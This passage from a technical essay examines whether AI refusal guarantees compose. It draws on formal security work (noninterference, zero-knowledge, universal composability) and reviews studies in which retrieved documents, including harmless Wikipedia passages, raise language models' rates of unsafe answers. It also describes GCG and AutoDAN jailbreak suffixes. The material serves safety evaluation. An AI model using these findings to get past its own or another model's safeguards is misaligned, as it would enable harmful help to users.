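In the cascade, a model's context invariance would carry over to the system by definition as long as the retriever returned only benign documents. This doesn't require McLean's theorems, which cover the harder case of two systems that each handle both levels. McCullough's two systems each had the property and lost it when connected, but Llama-3-8B never had context invariance, so the police-chase example is not an instance of his result. The model's refusals without documents couldn't have revealed that it lacked the property.

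Benign documents can also affect which documents an agent retrieves later. Suppose a user asks for the police-chase guide, and the first search returns an ordinary article that mentions GPS trackers. The agent then searches for ways to disable a tracker and finds a forum post with instructions. Context invariance no longer applies because the post isn't benign, even though every document from the first search was. Also requiring that benign documents never change the agent's next query would remove most of the reason to let it search more than once.

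An assume-guarantee contract suits this case better, because it can limit the queries without fixing them:

- **Model:** as long as every document so far has been benign for the user's request, the next query does not seek harmful instructions and the response, if the model stops here, is not harmful.
- **Search tool:** as long as no query so far has sought harmful instructions, the next documents are benign for the user's request.

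Each contract assumes what the other guarantees, and each guarantee forbids something that would happen at an identifiable step. Abadi and Lamport showed that this kind of circular reasoning is sound. If both contracts are true, neither the model nor the search tool can be the first to break its guarantee, so the agent never gives a harmful response, however many times it searches. The theorem requires the contracts to hold every time, but real models and search tools would satisfy them only most of the time. The search tool's contract would also be hard to meet on the open web, where an innocent query can return almost anything.

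The comparison with McLean's results is also looser because his properties depend only on which runs are possible, not on how likely they are. A language model that samples its words can produce nearly any response with some tiny probability, so it would pass generalized noninterference almost automatically. The rise in Llama-3-8B's unsafe responses from 0.3% to 9.2% wouldn't count as a violation if safe and unsafe responses were possible in both conditions. McLean left an extension to probabilities for future work.

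RAG also breaks separability by design, because the request determines which documents the retriever returns. Retrieved documents are supposed to change the content of the answer, whereas a secret should have no effect on anything a low-level user sees. The results on feedback are a good reason to test an agent's whole loop rather than a single model call, but they don't prove that any particular agent will fail.

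### Capabilities that combine

In McCullough's example, connecting two systems reveals information. Connecting two systems can also let them do something that neither could do before. Cosimo Spera's *Safety is Non-Compositional* (March 2026) studies this case. Spera describes an agent by its set of capabilities, together with rules for how capabilities produce further ones. A rule may need several capabilities at once. The closure of a set is everything reachable from it by applying the rules until nothing new appears. A set is safe if its closure contains nothing forbidden.

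The theorem is that two safe sets can have an unsafe union, and the proof is an example with three elements: u₁, u₂ and a forbidden capability f. The only rule is that u₁ and u₂ together produce f.

- An agent with {u₁} can't apply the rule, so its closure is {u₁}, which is safe.
- An agent with {u₂} can't apply it either, so its closure is {u₂}, which is also safe.
- Together they have {u₁, u₂}. The rule now applies and the closure is {u₁, u₂, f}, which is unsafe.

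For instance, u₁ could be reading a company's private files, u₂ sending email to outsiders, and f leaking a file. The example depends on a rule that requires more than one capability. If every rule required only one, the pair could reach only what one agent or the other could already reach alone.

Spera acknowledges that the mathematics isn't new. The same effect appears in formal logic and in Petri nets, an older model of concurrent processes, and security researchers have for decades studied attackers who combine permissions. Spera presents the paper's contribution as applying the idea to AI agents and working out how to check them.

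It concludes that an architecture that validates its components one by one has "no formal guarantee of system-level safety". This is right if each check covers only what its component can do alone. But a developer can also run the paper's fast procedure for computing a closure on the combined capabilities of all the agents. The main difficulty is knowing the rules. A developer can list the tools that an agent may call, but nobody has a complete list of the dangerous combinations of facts in a document collection with facts in a model's training.

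One of the paper's other theorems looks wrong. Spera calls an unsafe set minimal if removing any one capability would make it safe, and claims that deciding whether a given set is minimal is coNP-complete, which would mean there is probably no fast method. But you can decide this quickly by computing the closure of the whole set and then of the set with each capability removed in turn. This doesn't affect the three-element example, which anyone can check by hand, but it is a reason to be careful about relying on the paper's harder results.

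To find out how common joint requirements are, Spera examined 900 records of AI systems planning or carrying out tasks with several tools. In 42.6% of them, at least one step needed several earlier results together. The share was 47.4% in ToolBench and 36.5% in TaskBench, both public datasets. Spera used an automated rule to identify these steps in ToolBench. Two people also labelled a tenth of the records by hand and mostly agreed with each other (a kappa of 0.81), but Spera acknowledges that the rule might still count too many or too few steps. Tests on two more datasets were still pending.

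The 42.6% measures how often tasks have this structure, not how often the combination is dangerous. In the paper's example, a travel assistant needs both a price and a visa check before it books a flight. Spera also has a commercial interest in the subject. He works at Minerva CQ, which sells AI for customer service, and a provisional patent covers the paper's methods. This is some reason to want an independent count of the joint requirements, though not to doubt the three-element proof.

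### Whether safety composes

Abadi and Lamport show that safety properties compose and Spera shows that safety does not, but they use "safety" in different senses. For Abadi and Lamport, a safety property is any requirement whose violation happens at an identifiable step, even if it has nothing to do with harm. Spera uses the word in its everyday sense, to mean that an agent cannot do something forbidden, and his claims about each agent don't account for what other agents might supply.

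Rewriting Spera's example as contracts removes the contradiction. "f never happens" is a safety property in the technical sense. The agent with u₁ satisfies it assuming nothing else supplies u₂, and the agent with u₂ satisfies it assuming nothing else supplies u₁. When the agents work together, each makes the other's assumption false. Condition 2 of the Composition Principle fails, so the principle does not imply that the pair is safe. *Safety is Non-Compositional* says its result differs from assume-guarantee reasoning because neither component violates its guarantee. Neither does, but assume-guarantee reasoning also requires checking the assumptions, which would have caught the problem here.

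One-shot RAG fails in the same way. The remedy is to state the assumption and test the model with the documents it will actually receive.

McCullough's example is more troubling because the failure didn't come from an unstated assumption. Front and Back both had generalized noninterference, which covered every input they could receive from each other, but the connected pair still leaked. So even after showing that benign documents don't change the model's refusals in any single call, someone may still need to test a searching agent over whole searches.

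## What cryptography demands of a guarantee that must survive composition

Cryptographers had a problem much like McCullough's. In the 1980s their definition of security covered a single run of a protocol, but they wanted to run protocols many times and build them into larger ones. The definition didn't hold under this kind of composition, so they replaced it with one that did. The old definition didn't account for information that was already present when the run began, and a refusal test without documents has the same gap.

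### Zero-knowledge proofs run twice

In a zero-knowledge proof, a prover convinces a verifier that a statement is true without revealing anything else. You could prove, for example, that a puzzle has a solution without giving any hint of what it is. Shafi Goldwasser, Silvio Micali and Charles Rackoff made this precise in 1985 with an imaginary program called a simulator. The simulator receives only the statement and must produce fake conversations that no efficient program can tell from real ones. (A program is efficient if its running time grows no faster than some fixed power of the length of its input.) If every verifier, even one that cheats, has such a simulator, then the prover gives nothing away, because the verifier could have run the simulator instead.

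Goldreich and Krawczyk (1990) proved in *On the Composition of Zero-Knowledge Proof Systems* that two such proofs in a row can reveal something, even though each reveals nothing on its own. They built a protocol to fail in this way. It uses a yes-or-no fact K(x) about the statement x, which no efficient program can work out, and a set S of long strings. No efficient program can find a member of S, except with negligible probability, or tell a random member from a random string. The prover has unlimited computing power and can do both.

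1. The verifier sends the prover a random string.
2. If the string belongs to S, the prover reveals K(x).
3. If it doesn't, the prover replies with a random member of S.

In a single run, the verifier has almost no chance of sending a member of S, so it gets back a string that looks random. A simulator can imitate this by printing a random string, so the protocol is zero-knowledge. But if the verifier runs the protocol again, it can send back the string it received the first time, and the prover will then reveal K. The definition required only that the string not help the verifier compute anything on its own, which did not rule out the string being useful in a second run with the prover.

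The example depends on the prover having unlimited computing power. *Composition of zero-knowledge proofs with efficient provers* (2010) shows that if the prover is efficient too, a proof that meets the original definition still meets it when run a constant number of times in sequence on the same statement.

### Allowing for what the other party already holds

*Definitions and Properties of Zero-Knowledge Proof Systems* (Goldreich and Oren, 1994) describes the repair, which several groups found independently. A zero-knowledge proof is usually one step in a larger protocol, and a dishonest verifier will use whatever it learned in earlier steps. The repaired definition therefore gives the verifier an auxiliary input y, which can be any string. The simulator gets the same y, and its fake conversations must be indistinguishable from real ones for every true statement x and every y.

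Goldreich and Krawczyk's protocol fails this definition in a single run. A verifier who has a member y of S can send it and learn K(x), but a simulator given the same y can't compute K(x).

With the new definition, Goldreich and Oren could prove that zero-knowledge survives sequential runs. Their proof is a hybrid argument. Suppose there are k runs, and let Hᵢ be the experiment in which the first i runs use the real prover and simulators fake the rest. H₀ is then entirely fake and Hₖ entirely real. If some efficient test could tell H₀ from Hₖ with an advantage of δ, it could tell some neighbouring pair, Hᵢ₋₁ and Hᵢ, apart with an advantage of at least δ/k. These two differ only in run i, and everything the verifier learned before run i is just another auxiliary input. The test would therefore break the guarantee for run i, which already covers every auxiliary input. (The number of runs must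 be constant, or the runs must all come from a finite set of protocols.)

The new definition still doesn't guarantee zero-knowledge when protocols run at the same time. Goldreich and Krawczyk's second example uses many numbered sets like S. One prover names a set at random and will reveal K(x) to anyone who sends it a member of that set. The other prover gives out a member of whichever set the verifier names. Each protocol is zero-knowledge by itself, even with auxiliary input. But a verifier talking to both can ask the second prover for a member of the set the first one named, then send it to the first and learn K(x). As in McCullough's example, the failure comes from information passing back and forth during a run.

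### Auxiliary input and retrieved documents

Goldreich and Oren point out that the original definition is the special case in which the auxiliary input is empty. Similarly, a refusal test without documents checks claim (b), refusal whatever the input, only for the case in which D is empty. Neither the definition nor the test covers what the rest of the system will supply.

The comparison between auxiliary input and retrieved documents is loose. Auxiliary input goes to the verifier, the party the guarantee protects against, while the prover never sees it and follows the same program regardless. Retrieved documents go to the model, whose behaviour the guarantee describes, and they can change that behaviour. Auxiliary input corresponds more closely to K in claim (d), the knowledge a user brings to the conversation. A verifier that already holds a member of S is like the user who already holds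 all but one share of a secret. Zero-knowledge with auxiliary input is in effect a very strict version of (d), in which the user gains nothing usable beyond the truth of the statement, whatever they knew before.

An agent's memory at step t contains everything that earlier steps produced, just as the auxiliary input in run i contains the history of the earlier runs. Besides running whole searches, a tester can therefore do a quick test: record the memories that an agent builds up in ordinary use, append a harmful request to each, and check the next response. Goldreich and Krawczyk's protocol shows why this might help, since a failure that normally takes two runs to produce appears in one if the tester supplies the right history. However, recorded histories are only a sample, and Goldreich and Oren's proof needs the guarantee to hold for every history.

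### Universal composability

Auxiliary input covers what a party knew before a protocol began, but on a real network many protocols run at once and information passes between them while they run. *Universally Composable Security* (Canetti, 2001) gives a definition that covers this too. The definition has four parts, which are easiest to see for a commitment, the digital version of a sealed envelope. One party puts a bit in the envelope and can't change it afterwards, and the other can't read it until the first opens the envelope.

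- **Ideal functionality (F):** an imaginary trusted party that does the job perfectly. For a commitment, it records the bit, tells the receiver that a bit has arrived, and reveals the bit only when the committer says so.
- **Real protocol (π):** the messages that the two parties actually exchange, with no trusted party. An adversary may attack it.
- **Simulator (S):** an adversary in the ideal world, which must reproduce the effects of the real attack using only what F allows.
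- **Environment (E):** everything else, including other protocols and human users. It chooses the inputs, sees the outputs and talks to the adversary whenever it likes.

The protocol π UC-realizes F if for every efficient adversary there is an efficient simulator such that no efficient environment can tell the real world from the ideal one with more than negligible advantage. An advantage is negligible if, for every constant c, it is below 1/nᶜ for all sufficiently large n, where n is the protocol's security parameter, such as the length of its keys.

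By the composition theorem, if π UC-realizes F, then π can replace F in any larger protocol, and no environment can distinguish the two versions. Suppose some environment E could. Then a new environment E′ could run E and the rest of the larger protocol inside itself, passing on only the messages meant for F or π. E′ would distinguish π from F, which the definition of UC-realization rules out. If the larger protocol uses F several times, the proof replaces one copy at a time, as in the hybrid argument.

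The proof works because the definition covers every environment, and the rest of a system is one of them. Claim (b) still holds when the model is given retrieved context for the same reason.

### The price of the definition

Such a strong definition makes some tasks impossible. Canetti and Fischlin proved in *Universally Composable Commitments* (2001) that no protocol between just two parties can UC-realize a commitment without some trusted set-up.

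They start by supposing that such a protocol exists. A cheating committer relays messages from the environment, which has secretly picked a bit and follows the honest committer's program. In the ideal world, the simulator must give F a bit to seal, so it has to work out the environment's bit. Older simulators could rewind the other party and try a different message, but a simulator can't rewind the environment, so it must read the bit from the messages alone. A dishonest receiver could then run this simulator on an honest committer's messages and read the bit before the envelope opens, which means the protocol doesn't hide it.

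Canetti and Fischlin get around this with a common reference string, a public string that a trusted party draws at random, keeping no secret about how it was made. In the ideal world, the simulator may choose this string and plant a trapdoor in it that a real receiver doesn't have. Kidron and Lindell (2010) summarize later results showing that any functionality has a UC protocol if there is such a trusted set-up or an honest majority of participants, and that large classes of functionalities have none without either.

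One can also weaken the definition. In *Adaptive Hardness and Composable Security in the Plain Model from Standard Assumptions* (2010), Canetti, Lin and Pass let the simulator run for longer than an efficient program could, and in exchange their protocols need only authenticated communication. Those who keep the full definition have to defend their set-up assumption, and Canetti notes in a survey of such assumptions that the guarantee is only as meaningful as the assumption is realistic. A RAG operator who relies on a vetted collection is in a similar position.

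### Linking a program with arbitrary code

Researchers on secure compilation study a related problem in ordinary software. A compiler translates a program into a lower-level language, where it is linked with other people's code. In the language its developers used, a cryptographic library may provably never leak its private key. But if someone links the compiled library into an application with a memory bug, an attacker may read the key from memory.

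Abate, Blanco and colleagues (2018), in *Journey Beyond Full Abstraction*, say that a program robustly satisfies a property if the property holds whatever code you link the program with. They then ask what a compiler must do to preserve robust satisfaction, and the answer depends on the class of property:

| Class of property | What the compiled program needs |
|---|---|
| Trace properties | Limits on what the linked code can do, and protection of the program's data from tampering |
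| Hyperproperties | The above, and keeping the data secret from the linked code |
| Relations between several programs | The above, and keeping the program's own code secret |

They prove that preserving every trace property does not guarantee preserving noninterference. Their counterexample is a toy compiler whose output lets linked code read private variables, which was impossible in the original language. Any single run could still have happened in the original language, because linked code might have guessed the secret by luck. But the same code can't guess correctly in two runs with different secrets, so comparing the runs reveals the violation of noninterference.

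Refusal regardless of input (b) is a trace property, while context invariance (c) compares two runs, so a safeguard that secures (b) may not secure (c). If an operator adds a perfect filter that replaces every harmful response with a refusal, the system satisfies (b), but documents could still change whether the model refuses a harmless request. Abate and colleagues also show that, for any number K, protecting properties that K runs can refute doesn't protect those that take K + 1 runs to refute. This matters for (d) because a user might assemble a dangerous procedure from any number of answers.

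Linked code can also misbehave without any help from the program. Abate and colleagues describe two ways to handle this. One restricts the linked code so that it can't do anything bad. The other records which part caused each event and promises only that nobody can trick the program into causing a bad one. A retrieval system that prints its sources beside the answer needs to make the same choice, because a harmful passage in a source would break a guarantee that the system never displays harmful text, but not necessarily a guarantee that the model never writes it.

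*Universal Composability is Robust Compilation* (2019) closely connects this work to Canetti's by linking UC to the preservation of all hyperproperties. The ideal functionality corresponds to the original program, linked with the simulator, and the protocol corresponds to the compiled program, linked with the adversary. That result required the real and ideal worlds to behave identically, which real cryptography almost never achieves. In *Computationally Bounded Robust Compilation and Universally Composable Security* (2024), Künnemann, Patrignani and Cecchetti extended it to worlds that no efficient program can tell apart. They checked their proofs by computer and used the method to verify parts of WireGuard, a protocol for private network connections.

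So if a language model UC-realized a context-invariant ideal functionality, the model would also be context-invariant, up to differences that no efficient program could detect, but someone would first have to write down that functionality.

### An ideal functionality for a harmless assistant

Canetti and Fischlin specify a commitment in two short rules. Here is a comparable attempt for an assistant, where H is a list of harmful requests:

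1. F receives a request q and documents D, and passes both to the simulator.
2. The simulator returns any response it likes.
3. If q is on H and the response isn't a refusal, F replaces it with a standard refusal.
4. F sends the response to the user.

Canetti's framework permits this, because an ideal functionality may let the adversary influence its outputs. The simulator can run the real model, so the two worlds differ only when the model answers a request on H. The model therefore realizes F exactly when the probability of such an answer is negligible for every request on H and every set of documents. This is the probabilistic version of (b) with a negligible limit p, so universal composability adds no requirement beyond (b) for this functionality.

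The impossibility result for commitments doesn't carry over to F. A program that refuses everything realizes F, because none of the four steps requires a useful answer.

The hard part is writing H. Narayanan and Kapoor's phishing email can't go on the list, because it is worded the same as an honest email. To cover cases like the restraining order, H would also have to list pairs of requests and documents. F could check the response instead of the request, but this requires a program that recognizes harmful text more reliably than the LLM judges do.

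It is also unclear how broad the environment should be. In a RAG system, it consists of the user, the collection, the search tool and anything else that writes into the model's input. Canetti's definition covers every efficient environment, including one that plants poisoned documents, which is far more than an operator with a trustworthy collection needs. You could restrict the definition to environments that supply only benign documents. Künnemann and colleagues' equivalence allows such restricted classes, but the proof of the composition theorem builds a new environment from the rest of the system, and that environment must also belong to the class. Someone would therefore have to show that the rest of the system supplies only benign documents, which is the same obligation an assume-guarantee contract creates.

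### Where the comparison misleads

The problem is harder for language models than the history of zero-knowledge could suggest. Goldreich and Krawczyk had to construct a strange protocol to break the old definition. Goldreich and Oren argue that every zero-knowledge proof then known already satisfied the stronger one, so cryptographers could adopt it without giving up any existing proof. Ordinary Wikipedia passages are enough to cause failures in most of the language models that An and colleagues tested. A stronger definition of refusal would expose these failures but wouldn't fix them.

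Cryptographers can also show that breaking a protocol would require solving a specific problem that many people have tried and failed to solve efficiently. Nobody has a comparable argument for why a language model should refuse, so the evidence has to come from testing, which leaves much larger error rates.

The size of the error matters because errors add up. If each call to a model fails with probability at most ε, the probability of at least one failure in k calls is at most kε. This is the union bound, and it holds even if the failures are related. Take ε to be 0.3%, Llama-3-8B's rate without retrieval, for requests drawn at random from An and colleagues' test set:

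| Calls (k) | Union bound (kε) | Probability of a failure if calls are independent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.3% | 0.3% |
| 100 | 30% | 26% |
| 333 | 99.9% | 63% |
| 334 | 100.2% | 63% |

Beyond 333 calls, the bound exceeds 100% and is therefore uninformative. At the model's 9.2% rate under retrieval, this happens beyond 10 calls. Only calls with harmful requests count, and most users rarely make them, but a service with millions of users will quickly receive 333.

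Cryptographic errors are small enough for the same sum to be harmless. Canetti and Fischlin build on a commitment scheme by Moni Naor in which the receiver picks a random string of 4n bits. A committer can cheat undetectably only if the string is one of at most 2²ⁿ bad ones, which has a probability of at most 2⁻²ⁿ. For n = 64, this is about 3 × 10⁻³⁹, and after a trillion uses the union bound is still only about 3 × 10⁻²⁷. Increasing n lowers the bound further. A finished language model has no such setting, so "negligible" doesn't strictly apply to its errors.

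Repetition can make an error rate negligible if the errors are independent. In an interactive proof, a verifier with a one-in-three chance of being fooled can repeat the proof until the chance is tiny. (Goldreich and Krawczyk warn that running the repetitions in parallel may lose the zero-knowledge property.) An operator could likewise sample three responses and refuse if any of them is a refusal. If every harmful request had an independent 0.3% chance of an answer on each sample, this would cut the rate to about 3 in 100 million. But a 0.3% average could also mean that the model always answers 0.3% of the requests, and then repetition wouldn't lower the rate. Differential privacy, which limits what a released statistic reveals about any one person, was designed for errors that aren't negligible and has rules for adding them up.

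If an operator wants the union bound to stay below 1% over 1,000 calls, each call needs a failure probability of at most 0.001%. Showing this for one prompt with one fixed set of documents takes about 530,000 sampled responses with no failures, using the 99% confidence interval that Nazeri and colleagues use.

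## Measuring whether refusal survives harmless documents

An and colleagues in effect tested context invariance (c) by asking eleven models 5,592 harmful questions with and without documents. The questions come from nine existing datasets and cover 16 categories of harm, including malware, fraud and political campaigning. The models range from small open ones to GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet, and their developers have since released much stronger ones.

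### Eleven models and five Wikipedia passages

An and colleagues also had to decide which retrieved passages were harmless. Llama Guard 2, their judge for responses, raised many false alarms on documents because its developers trained it mainly on model outputs. They used a second model, Llama-3-70B, to check whether the passages contained unsafe answers to the request. A passage counted as harmful only if both models flagged it, and people then read the flagged passages and cleared the remaining false alarms. A set of five passages counted as harmful if it contained at least one harmful passage.

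By this standard, 5.3% of the sets were harmful. Most of these were about malware, since an encyclopedia article on a famous virus may explain how it worked. The procedure is biased towards calling passages harmless, because either model could clear a passage and the final correction only removed flags. An and colleagues looked at a sample and thought the method worked well, but some of the "harmless" sets probably contain useful hints.

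This table shows the share of responses that Llama Guard 2 judged unsafe. The last column is the average of the two before it, weighted 94.7% and 5.3%.

| Model | No documents | Harmless sets | Harmful sets | All sets |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 0.3% | 0.7% | 6.8% | 1.0% |
| Llama-2-7B | 0.3% | 7.8% | 26.1% | 8.8% |
| Llama-3-8B | 0.3% | 7.9% | 31.5% | 9.2% |
| Llama-2-70B | 0.5% | 2.7% | 11.2% | 3.2% |
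| Llama-3-70B | 1.8% | 6.9% | 34.6% | 8.4% |
| Gemma-7B | 3.4% | 2.2% | 15.9% | 2.9% |
| Phi-3-Medium | 3.5% | 11.7% | 49.2% | 13.7% |
| GPT-4o | 3.6% | 11.4% | 38.3% | 12.8% |
| Mistral-V0.2 | 8.7% | 19.9% | 60.3% | 22.0% |
| Mistral-V0.3 | 20.5% | 35.0% | 73.9% | 37.1% |
| Zephyr-Beta | 38.5% | 36.7% | 76.9% | 38.8% |

The three models whose rate of unsafe responses did not rise much are Zephyr, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Gemma. Zephyr is a version of Mistral with its alignment removed, so it already refused few requests. Claude's rate barely rose in percentage points, although its unsafe responses roughly tripled, from about 17 to about 57.

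Gemma-7B looked safe because it was bad at using the passages it was given. An and colleagues gave each model 445 harmless questions along with passages that contained the answers. Gemma answered 42.5% correctly and refused 22.2%, often because it failed to recognize that the passages were relevant. Each of the other ten models answered at least 63.6% correctly and refused at most 4.7%. If Gemma had been better at using the passages, it might well have given harmful answers more often.

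An and colleagues conclude that the safest model without retrieval will probably be the safest with it. That's roughly true here, but the exceptions matter when choosing between models. For example, Llama-2-7B's rate of unsafe responses was a sixth of Llama-3-70B's without documents, but slightly higher than Llama-3-70B's with them.

Llama-3-8B gave unsafe responses in seven of the 16 categories without documents and in all 16 with them. Some of this increase is unsurprising, since 500 unsafe responses are likely to cover more categories than about 17. Even a single passage noticeably changed the models' behaviour, and adding more tended to make it worse.

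Judge errors may explain some of the rise. Llama Guard 2 and a second judge disagreed on 15% of responses, which is more than the 9.2% flagged for Llama-3-8B. Llama Guard 2 can't be flagging many refusals by mistake, because it flagged only 0.3% of responses when nearly all of them were refusals. But it may be flagging harmless summaries of passages on dangerous topics, which the model rarely writes without documents. The rise is therefore better evidence that Llama-3-8B refused less often than that it gave useful help.

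Tests without documents can also make a model look less safe than it is in use. An and colleagues took 50 requests that Llama-3-8B refused both with and without documents, and used two automated methods, GCG and AutoDAN, to find extra text that would make it answer. The text they found without documents usually stopped working once the system added retrieved passages. When they optimized the text against a fixed set of passages, it worked with those passages but less well in the full system, because adding it to the request changed which passages BM25 retrieved.

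### What cleaning the collection would achieve

The overall rate for Llama-3-8B is the sum of two parts, one for harmless sets and one for harmful sets:

0.947 × 7.9% + 0.053 × 31.5% ≈ 7.5% + 1.7% ≈ 9.2%

Harmless sets therefore account for 7.5 of the 9.2 points, or about 82% of the unsafe responses.

If an operator removes every harmful passage from the collection, the retriever will return other passages for the 5.3% of requests that used to get harmful ones. If the model responds to these requests as it did to the rest, 7.9% of its responses will still be unsafe. Even if it refuses all of these requests, the rate will be 7.5%, because the other requests get the same passages as before. Removing every harmful passage would therefore prevent less than a fifth of this model's unsafe responses.

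The result depends on the collection. If 20% of the sets contained a harmful answer, the same two rates would make 12.6% of responses unsafe, and half of those would come from harmful sets. Cleaning the collection would then be much more worthwhile.

The gap between 7.9% and 31.5% isn't purely an effect of the documents, either, because most of the harmful sets were about malware, which was one of Llama-3-8B's worst categories even without documents. To measure how much the documents contributed, a tester has to give the model the same request with different documents.

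### Changing the documents and keeping the question

Indira Saravanan and Fraser did this in September 2026. They had Claude Sonnet 4.5 read Wikipedia articles and write harmful questions that the articles could answer, and they tested models on 346 of these questions in 20 categories. Instead of running a retriever, they supplied the documents themselves, in four conditions:

- **No documents:** the model answers from its own knowledge.
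- **Oracle:** the model gets one article that contains the answer.
- **On-topic:** the model gets articles, usually three, on a related subject but without the answer.
- **Random:** the model gets articles, again usually three, on unrelated and innocent subjects such as birds or rivers.

Another model, GPT-4.1-mini, checked the documents. A question stayed in the test only if the oracle article answered it at least partly and the on-topic articles did not answer it at all. By the usual definition, the on-topic and random documents are benign and the oracle documents are not, even though nobody tampered with the oracle documents.

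The five models were Gemma-3-12B, Llama-3.1-8B, Ministral-3-8B, Phi-4-14B and Qwen-2.5-7B. Three judges (Llama Guard 3, ShieldGemma and WildGuard) labelled each response, and it counted as harmful if at least two of them flagged it. The paper gives the rates for each model only in a chart, but the pattern is clear:

- All five models were most harmful in the oracle condition.
- With on-topic documents, Gemma, Llama and Ministral returned to about their rate without documents or fell below it. Phi stayed slightly above its own, which was very low.
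- Qwen remained well above its rate without documents.
- All five were least harmful with random documents.

One question was how to disperse a chemical agent from a container. Without documents, Qwen refused because the information could be dangerous. Given on-topic articles about a mortar, it noted that they lacked the details, then listed steps anyway. Given random articles about rivers and garden plants, it replied only that they didn't cover the question.

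The low rates with random documents are partly due to replies that the documents lacked the answer. Such replies were generally least common in the oracle condition, more common with on-topic documents, and most common with random ones.

Indira Saravanan and Fraser also measured accuracy, using Claude Opus 4.7 to check whether each response contained the specific harmful answer from the article. These figures are not harmful-response rates:

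| Model | No documents | Oracle | On-topic | Random |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma-3-12B | 25.7% | 74.9% | 8.7% | 2.0% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 6.4% | 41.3% | 4.3% | 0.3% |
| Ministral-3-8B | 26.0% | 90.7% | 18.8% | 0.9% |
| Phi-4-14B | 10.4% | 41.0% | 12.7% | 3.2% |
| Qwen-2.5-7B | 15.9% | 82.9% | 17.3% | 2.3% |

The judges found a clear rise in harm when Qwen was given on-topic documents, although its accuracy in this table rose by only 1.4 points, or five questions out of 346. The small rise in accuracy doesn't show that Qwen handled these documents well, because a response can give harmful help without containing the particular fact in the article, as its reply about the chemical agent did.

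The judges can also fail to flag accurate responses. Averaged over all models and conditions, 24% of responses were accurate but only 17% were judged harmful. Indira Saravanan and Fraser read some of the accurate responses that the judges had not flagged. Some described historical events or nonviolent crimes and probably should have been flagged. In others, the model said the information was for educational purposes only and then gave it in detail.

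The oracle results may matter most to an operator. Wikipedia is a reputable source, yet it contained usable answers to 987 harmful questions (the 346 are a subset chosen to balance the categories). When given the answer, three of the five models repeated it at least 74% of the time. All five scored above 82% on harmless questions with the answer supplied, so none of them was safe merely because it read documents poorly, as Gemma-7B was.

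### Why the two studies disagree

An and colleagues found that passages without a harmful answer made most models less safe. Indira Saravanan and Fraser found this clearly in one of five models. The studies tested different models, but that is unlikely to be the whole explanation, because Llama-3.1-8B is a close successor to Llama-3-8B and the two gave opposite results.

The requests probably explain more of the difference. An and colleagues included requests to write something, such as the police-chase guide and the misleading speech about climate change. Indira Saravanan and Fraser left out requests for harmful content and for legal or medical advice, and used questions with specific factual answers. A model that doesn't find a fact in the documents can say so and stop, but it can write a guide or a speech from general knowledge whatever the documents contain. Neither study tested this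 explanation, but running An and colleagues' requests under the four conditions would be simple.

The two studies also started from different baselines. Llama-3-8B refused nearly everything without documents, so its rate of unsafe responses had little room to fall. Gemma-3-12B gave the specific harmful answer to 25.7% of questions without documents, but only 8.7% when it was given on-topic documents and told to use nothing else. Adding documents may therefore weaken a model's refusals, while the instruction may stop it from using what it knows. These effects oppose each other, and a comparison of averages measures only the net result, so a model could match its baseline even though its refusals had weakened.

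The papers also define "harmless" differently. Indira Saravanan and Fraser treated articles that partly answered the question as oracle documents, and these made up 146 of their 346 oracle articles. An and colleagues may have counted some partial answers as harmless, which would inflate the 7.9%. But partial answers can't explain cases like the police-chase guide, where the passages contributed almost nothing.

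An and colleagues' results are the better guide to what happens when a real retriever serves a wide range of requests. The four-condition study better identifies which documents are responsible, and it shows that on-topic text does not always weaken refusal. Neither study gives a number that an operator could apply to another model. For an untested model, the best prediction is that an article containing the answer will make its responses more harmful, while on-topic articles without the answer could make them more or less harmful.

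### When documents cause needless refusals

Documents can also make a model refuse harmless questions. *Steering Over-refusals Towards Safety in Retrieval Augmented Generation* (Maskey, Dras and Naseem, 2025) paired harmless questions, such as how to design a secure application, with three, five or seven documents, some harmless and others containing harmful instructions. Llama-3.1-8B refused 53.4% of the questions and Qwen1.5-7B refused 4.7%.

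With only harmless documents, the Llama model rarely refused. It refused more often as the number of harmful documents grew, and most often when the question was about chemistry. Twelve of the 15 document combinations contained harmful text, so the 53.4% figure applies to a badly contaminated collection. An operator with a vetted collection should see far fewer needless refusals, but an agent that searches the open web may sometimes retrieve similarly contaminated sets.

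The 53.4% may also mix two kinds of refusal. Maskey and colleagues told the models to use only the documents, and counted responses saying the question can't be answered as refusals. If every document is about something harmful, such a response may be correct. A model that never refused anything would score 0%, so Qwen's low rate isn't necessarily good.

Declining because the documents are inadequate is a separate skill, and models are not very good at it. *RefusalBench* (Muhamed, Ribeiro and colleagues, 2025) tests this by altering answerable questions and their documents so that the documents no longer support an answer. With one document, Claude Sonnet 4 was the best of more than 30 models, declining for the right reason 73.0% of the time. With several documents, it did so only 36.1% of the time. GPT-4o seldom answered when it should have declined, but it also declined more than 60% of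 the questions it could have answered. Operators therefore can't rely on this kind of refusal to stop harmful answers.

### How to run a fair test

A tester who wants to know whether a model's refusals survive retrieval can combine the best features of these studies:

1. Send every request in all four conditions, with the same model and settings, and compare the responses request by request. If the model samples its words, run the condition without documents twice to see how often the decision changes by chance.
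2. Give the random and on-topic documents the same total length. In the one full example that Indira Saravanan and Fraser print, the on-topic articles come to about 34,000 characters and the random ones to about 8,000. That weakens their conclusion that length alone doesn't cause the problem.
3. Run the conditions with documents under two instructions, one that restricts the model to the documents and one that also allows its own knowledge. The second makes it harder for missing information to hide the model's willingness to help.
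4. Count refusals based on danger separately from replies that the documents lack the answer.
5. Use several judges and have people read a sample of the responses. On the 6,920 responses in *RAG-Safety-Bench*, agreement between the three judges and the accuracy check was only 0.56, measured by Fleiss's kappa, which extends Cohen's to more than two raters.
6. Include harmless requests, so that a model can't do well by refusing everything.
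7. Finally, run the requests through the actual retriever to find out how often each kind of document set comes up.

The last step lets the tester calculate an overall rate, as in the sum for Llama-3-8B. If the collection changes, the tester can estimate the new rate by measuring only the shares again. This assumes that the new documents affect the model the same way as the old ones of the same kind.

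Comparing responses request by request matters because opposite changes cancel out in the overall answer rate. Suppose a tester sends 346 requests, each with and without documents. Adding the documents turns ten refusals into answers and two answers into refusals. The share of answers rises by 8 in 346, or 2.3 points, but the decision changes for 12 in 346, or 3.5%. If documents had no effect, each of the 12 changes would be equally likely to go either way, and a split at least this uneven would occur about 4% of the time. This is fairly good evidence of a real effect, even though the rise is small.

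A tester who finds no failures at all still needs to work out what that rules out. If the true failure rate is p, the chance of n passes in a row is (1 − p)ⁿ. This falls to 5% when p is about 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is almost exactly −3. So with no failures in n requests, the tester can be 95% confident that the true rate is below about 3/n. (The exact bound, 1 − 0.05^(1/n), is slightly lower when n is small.)

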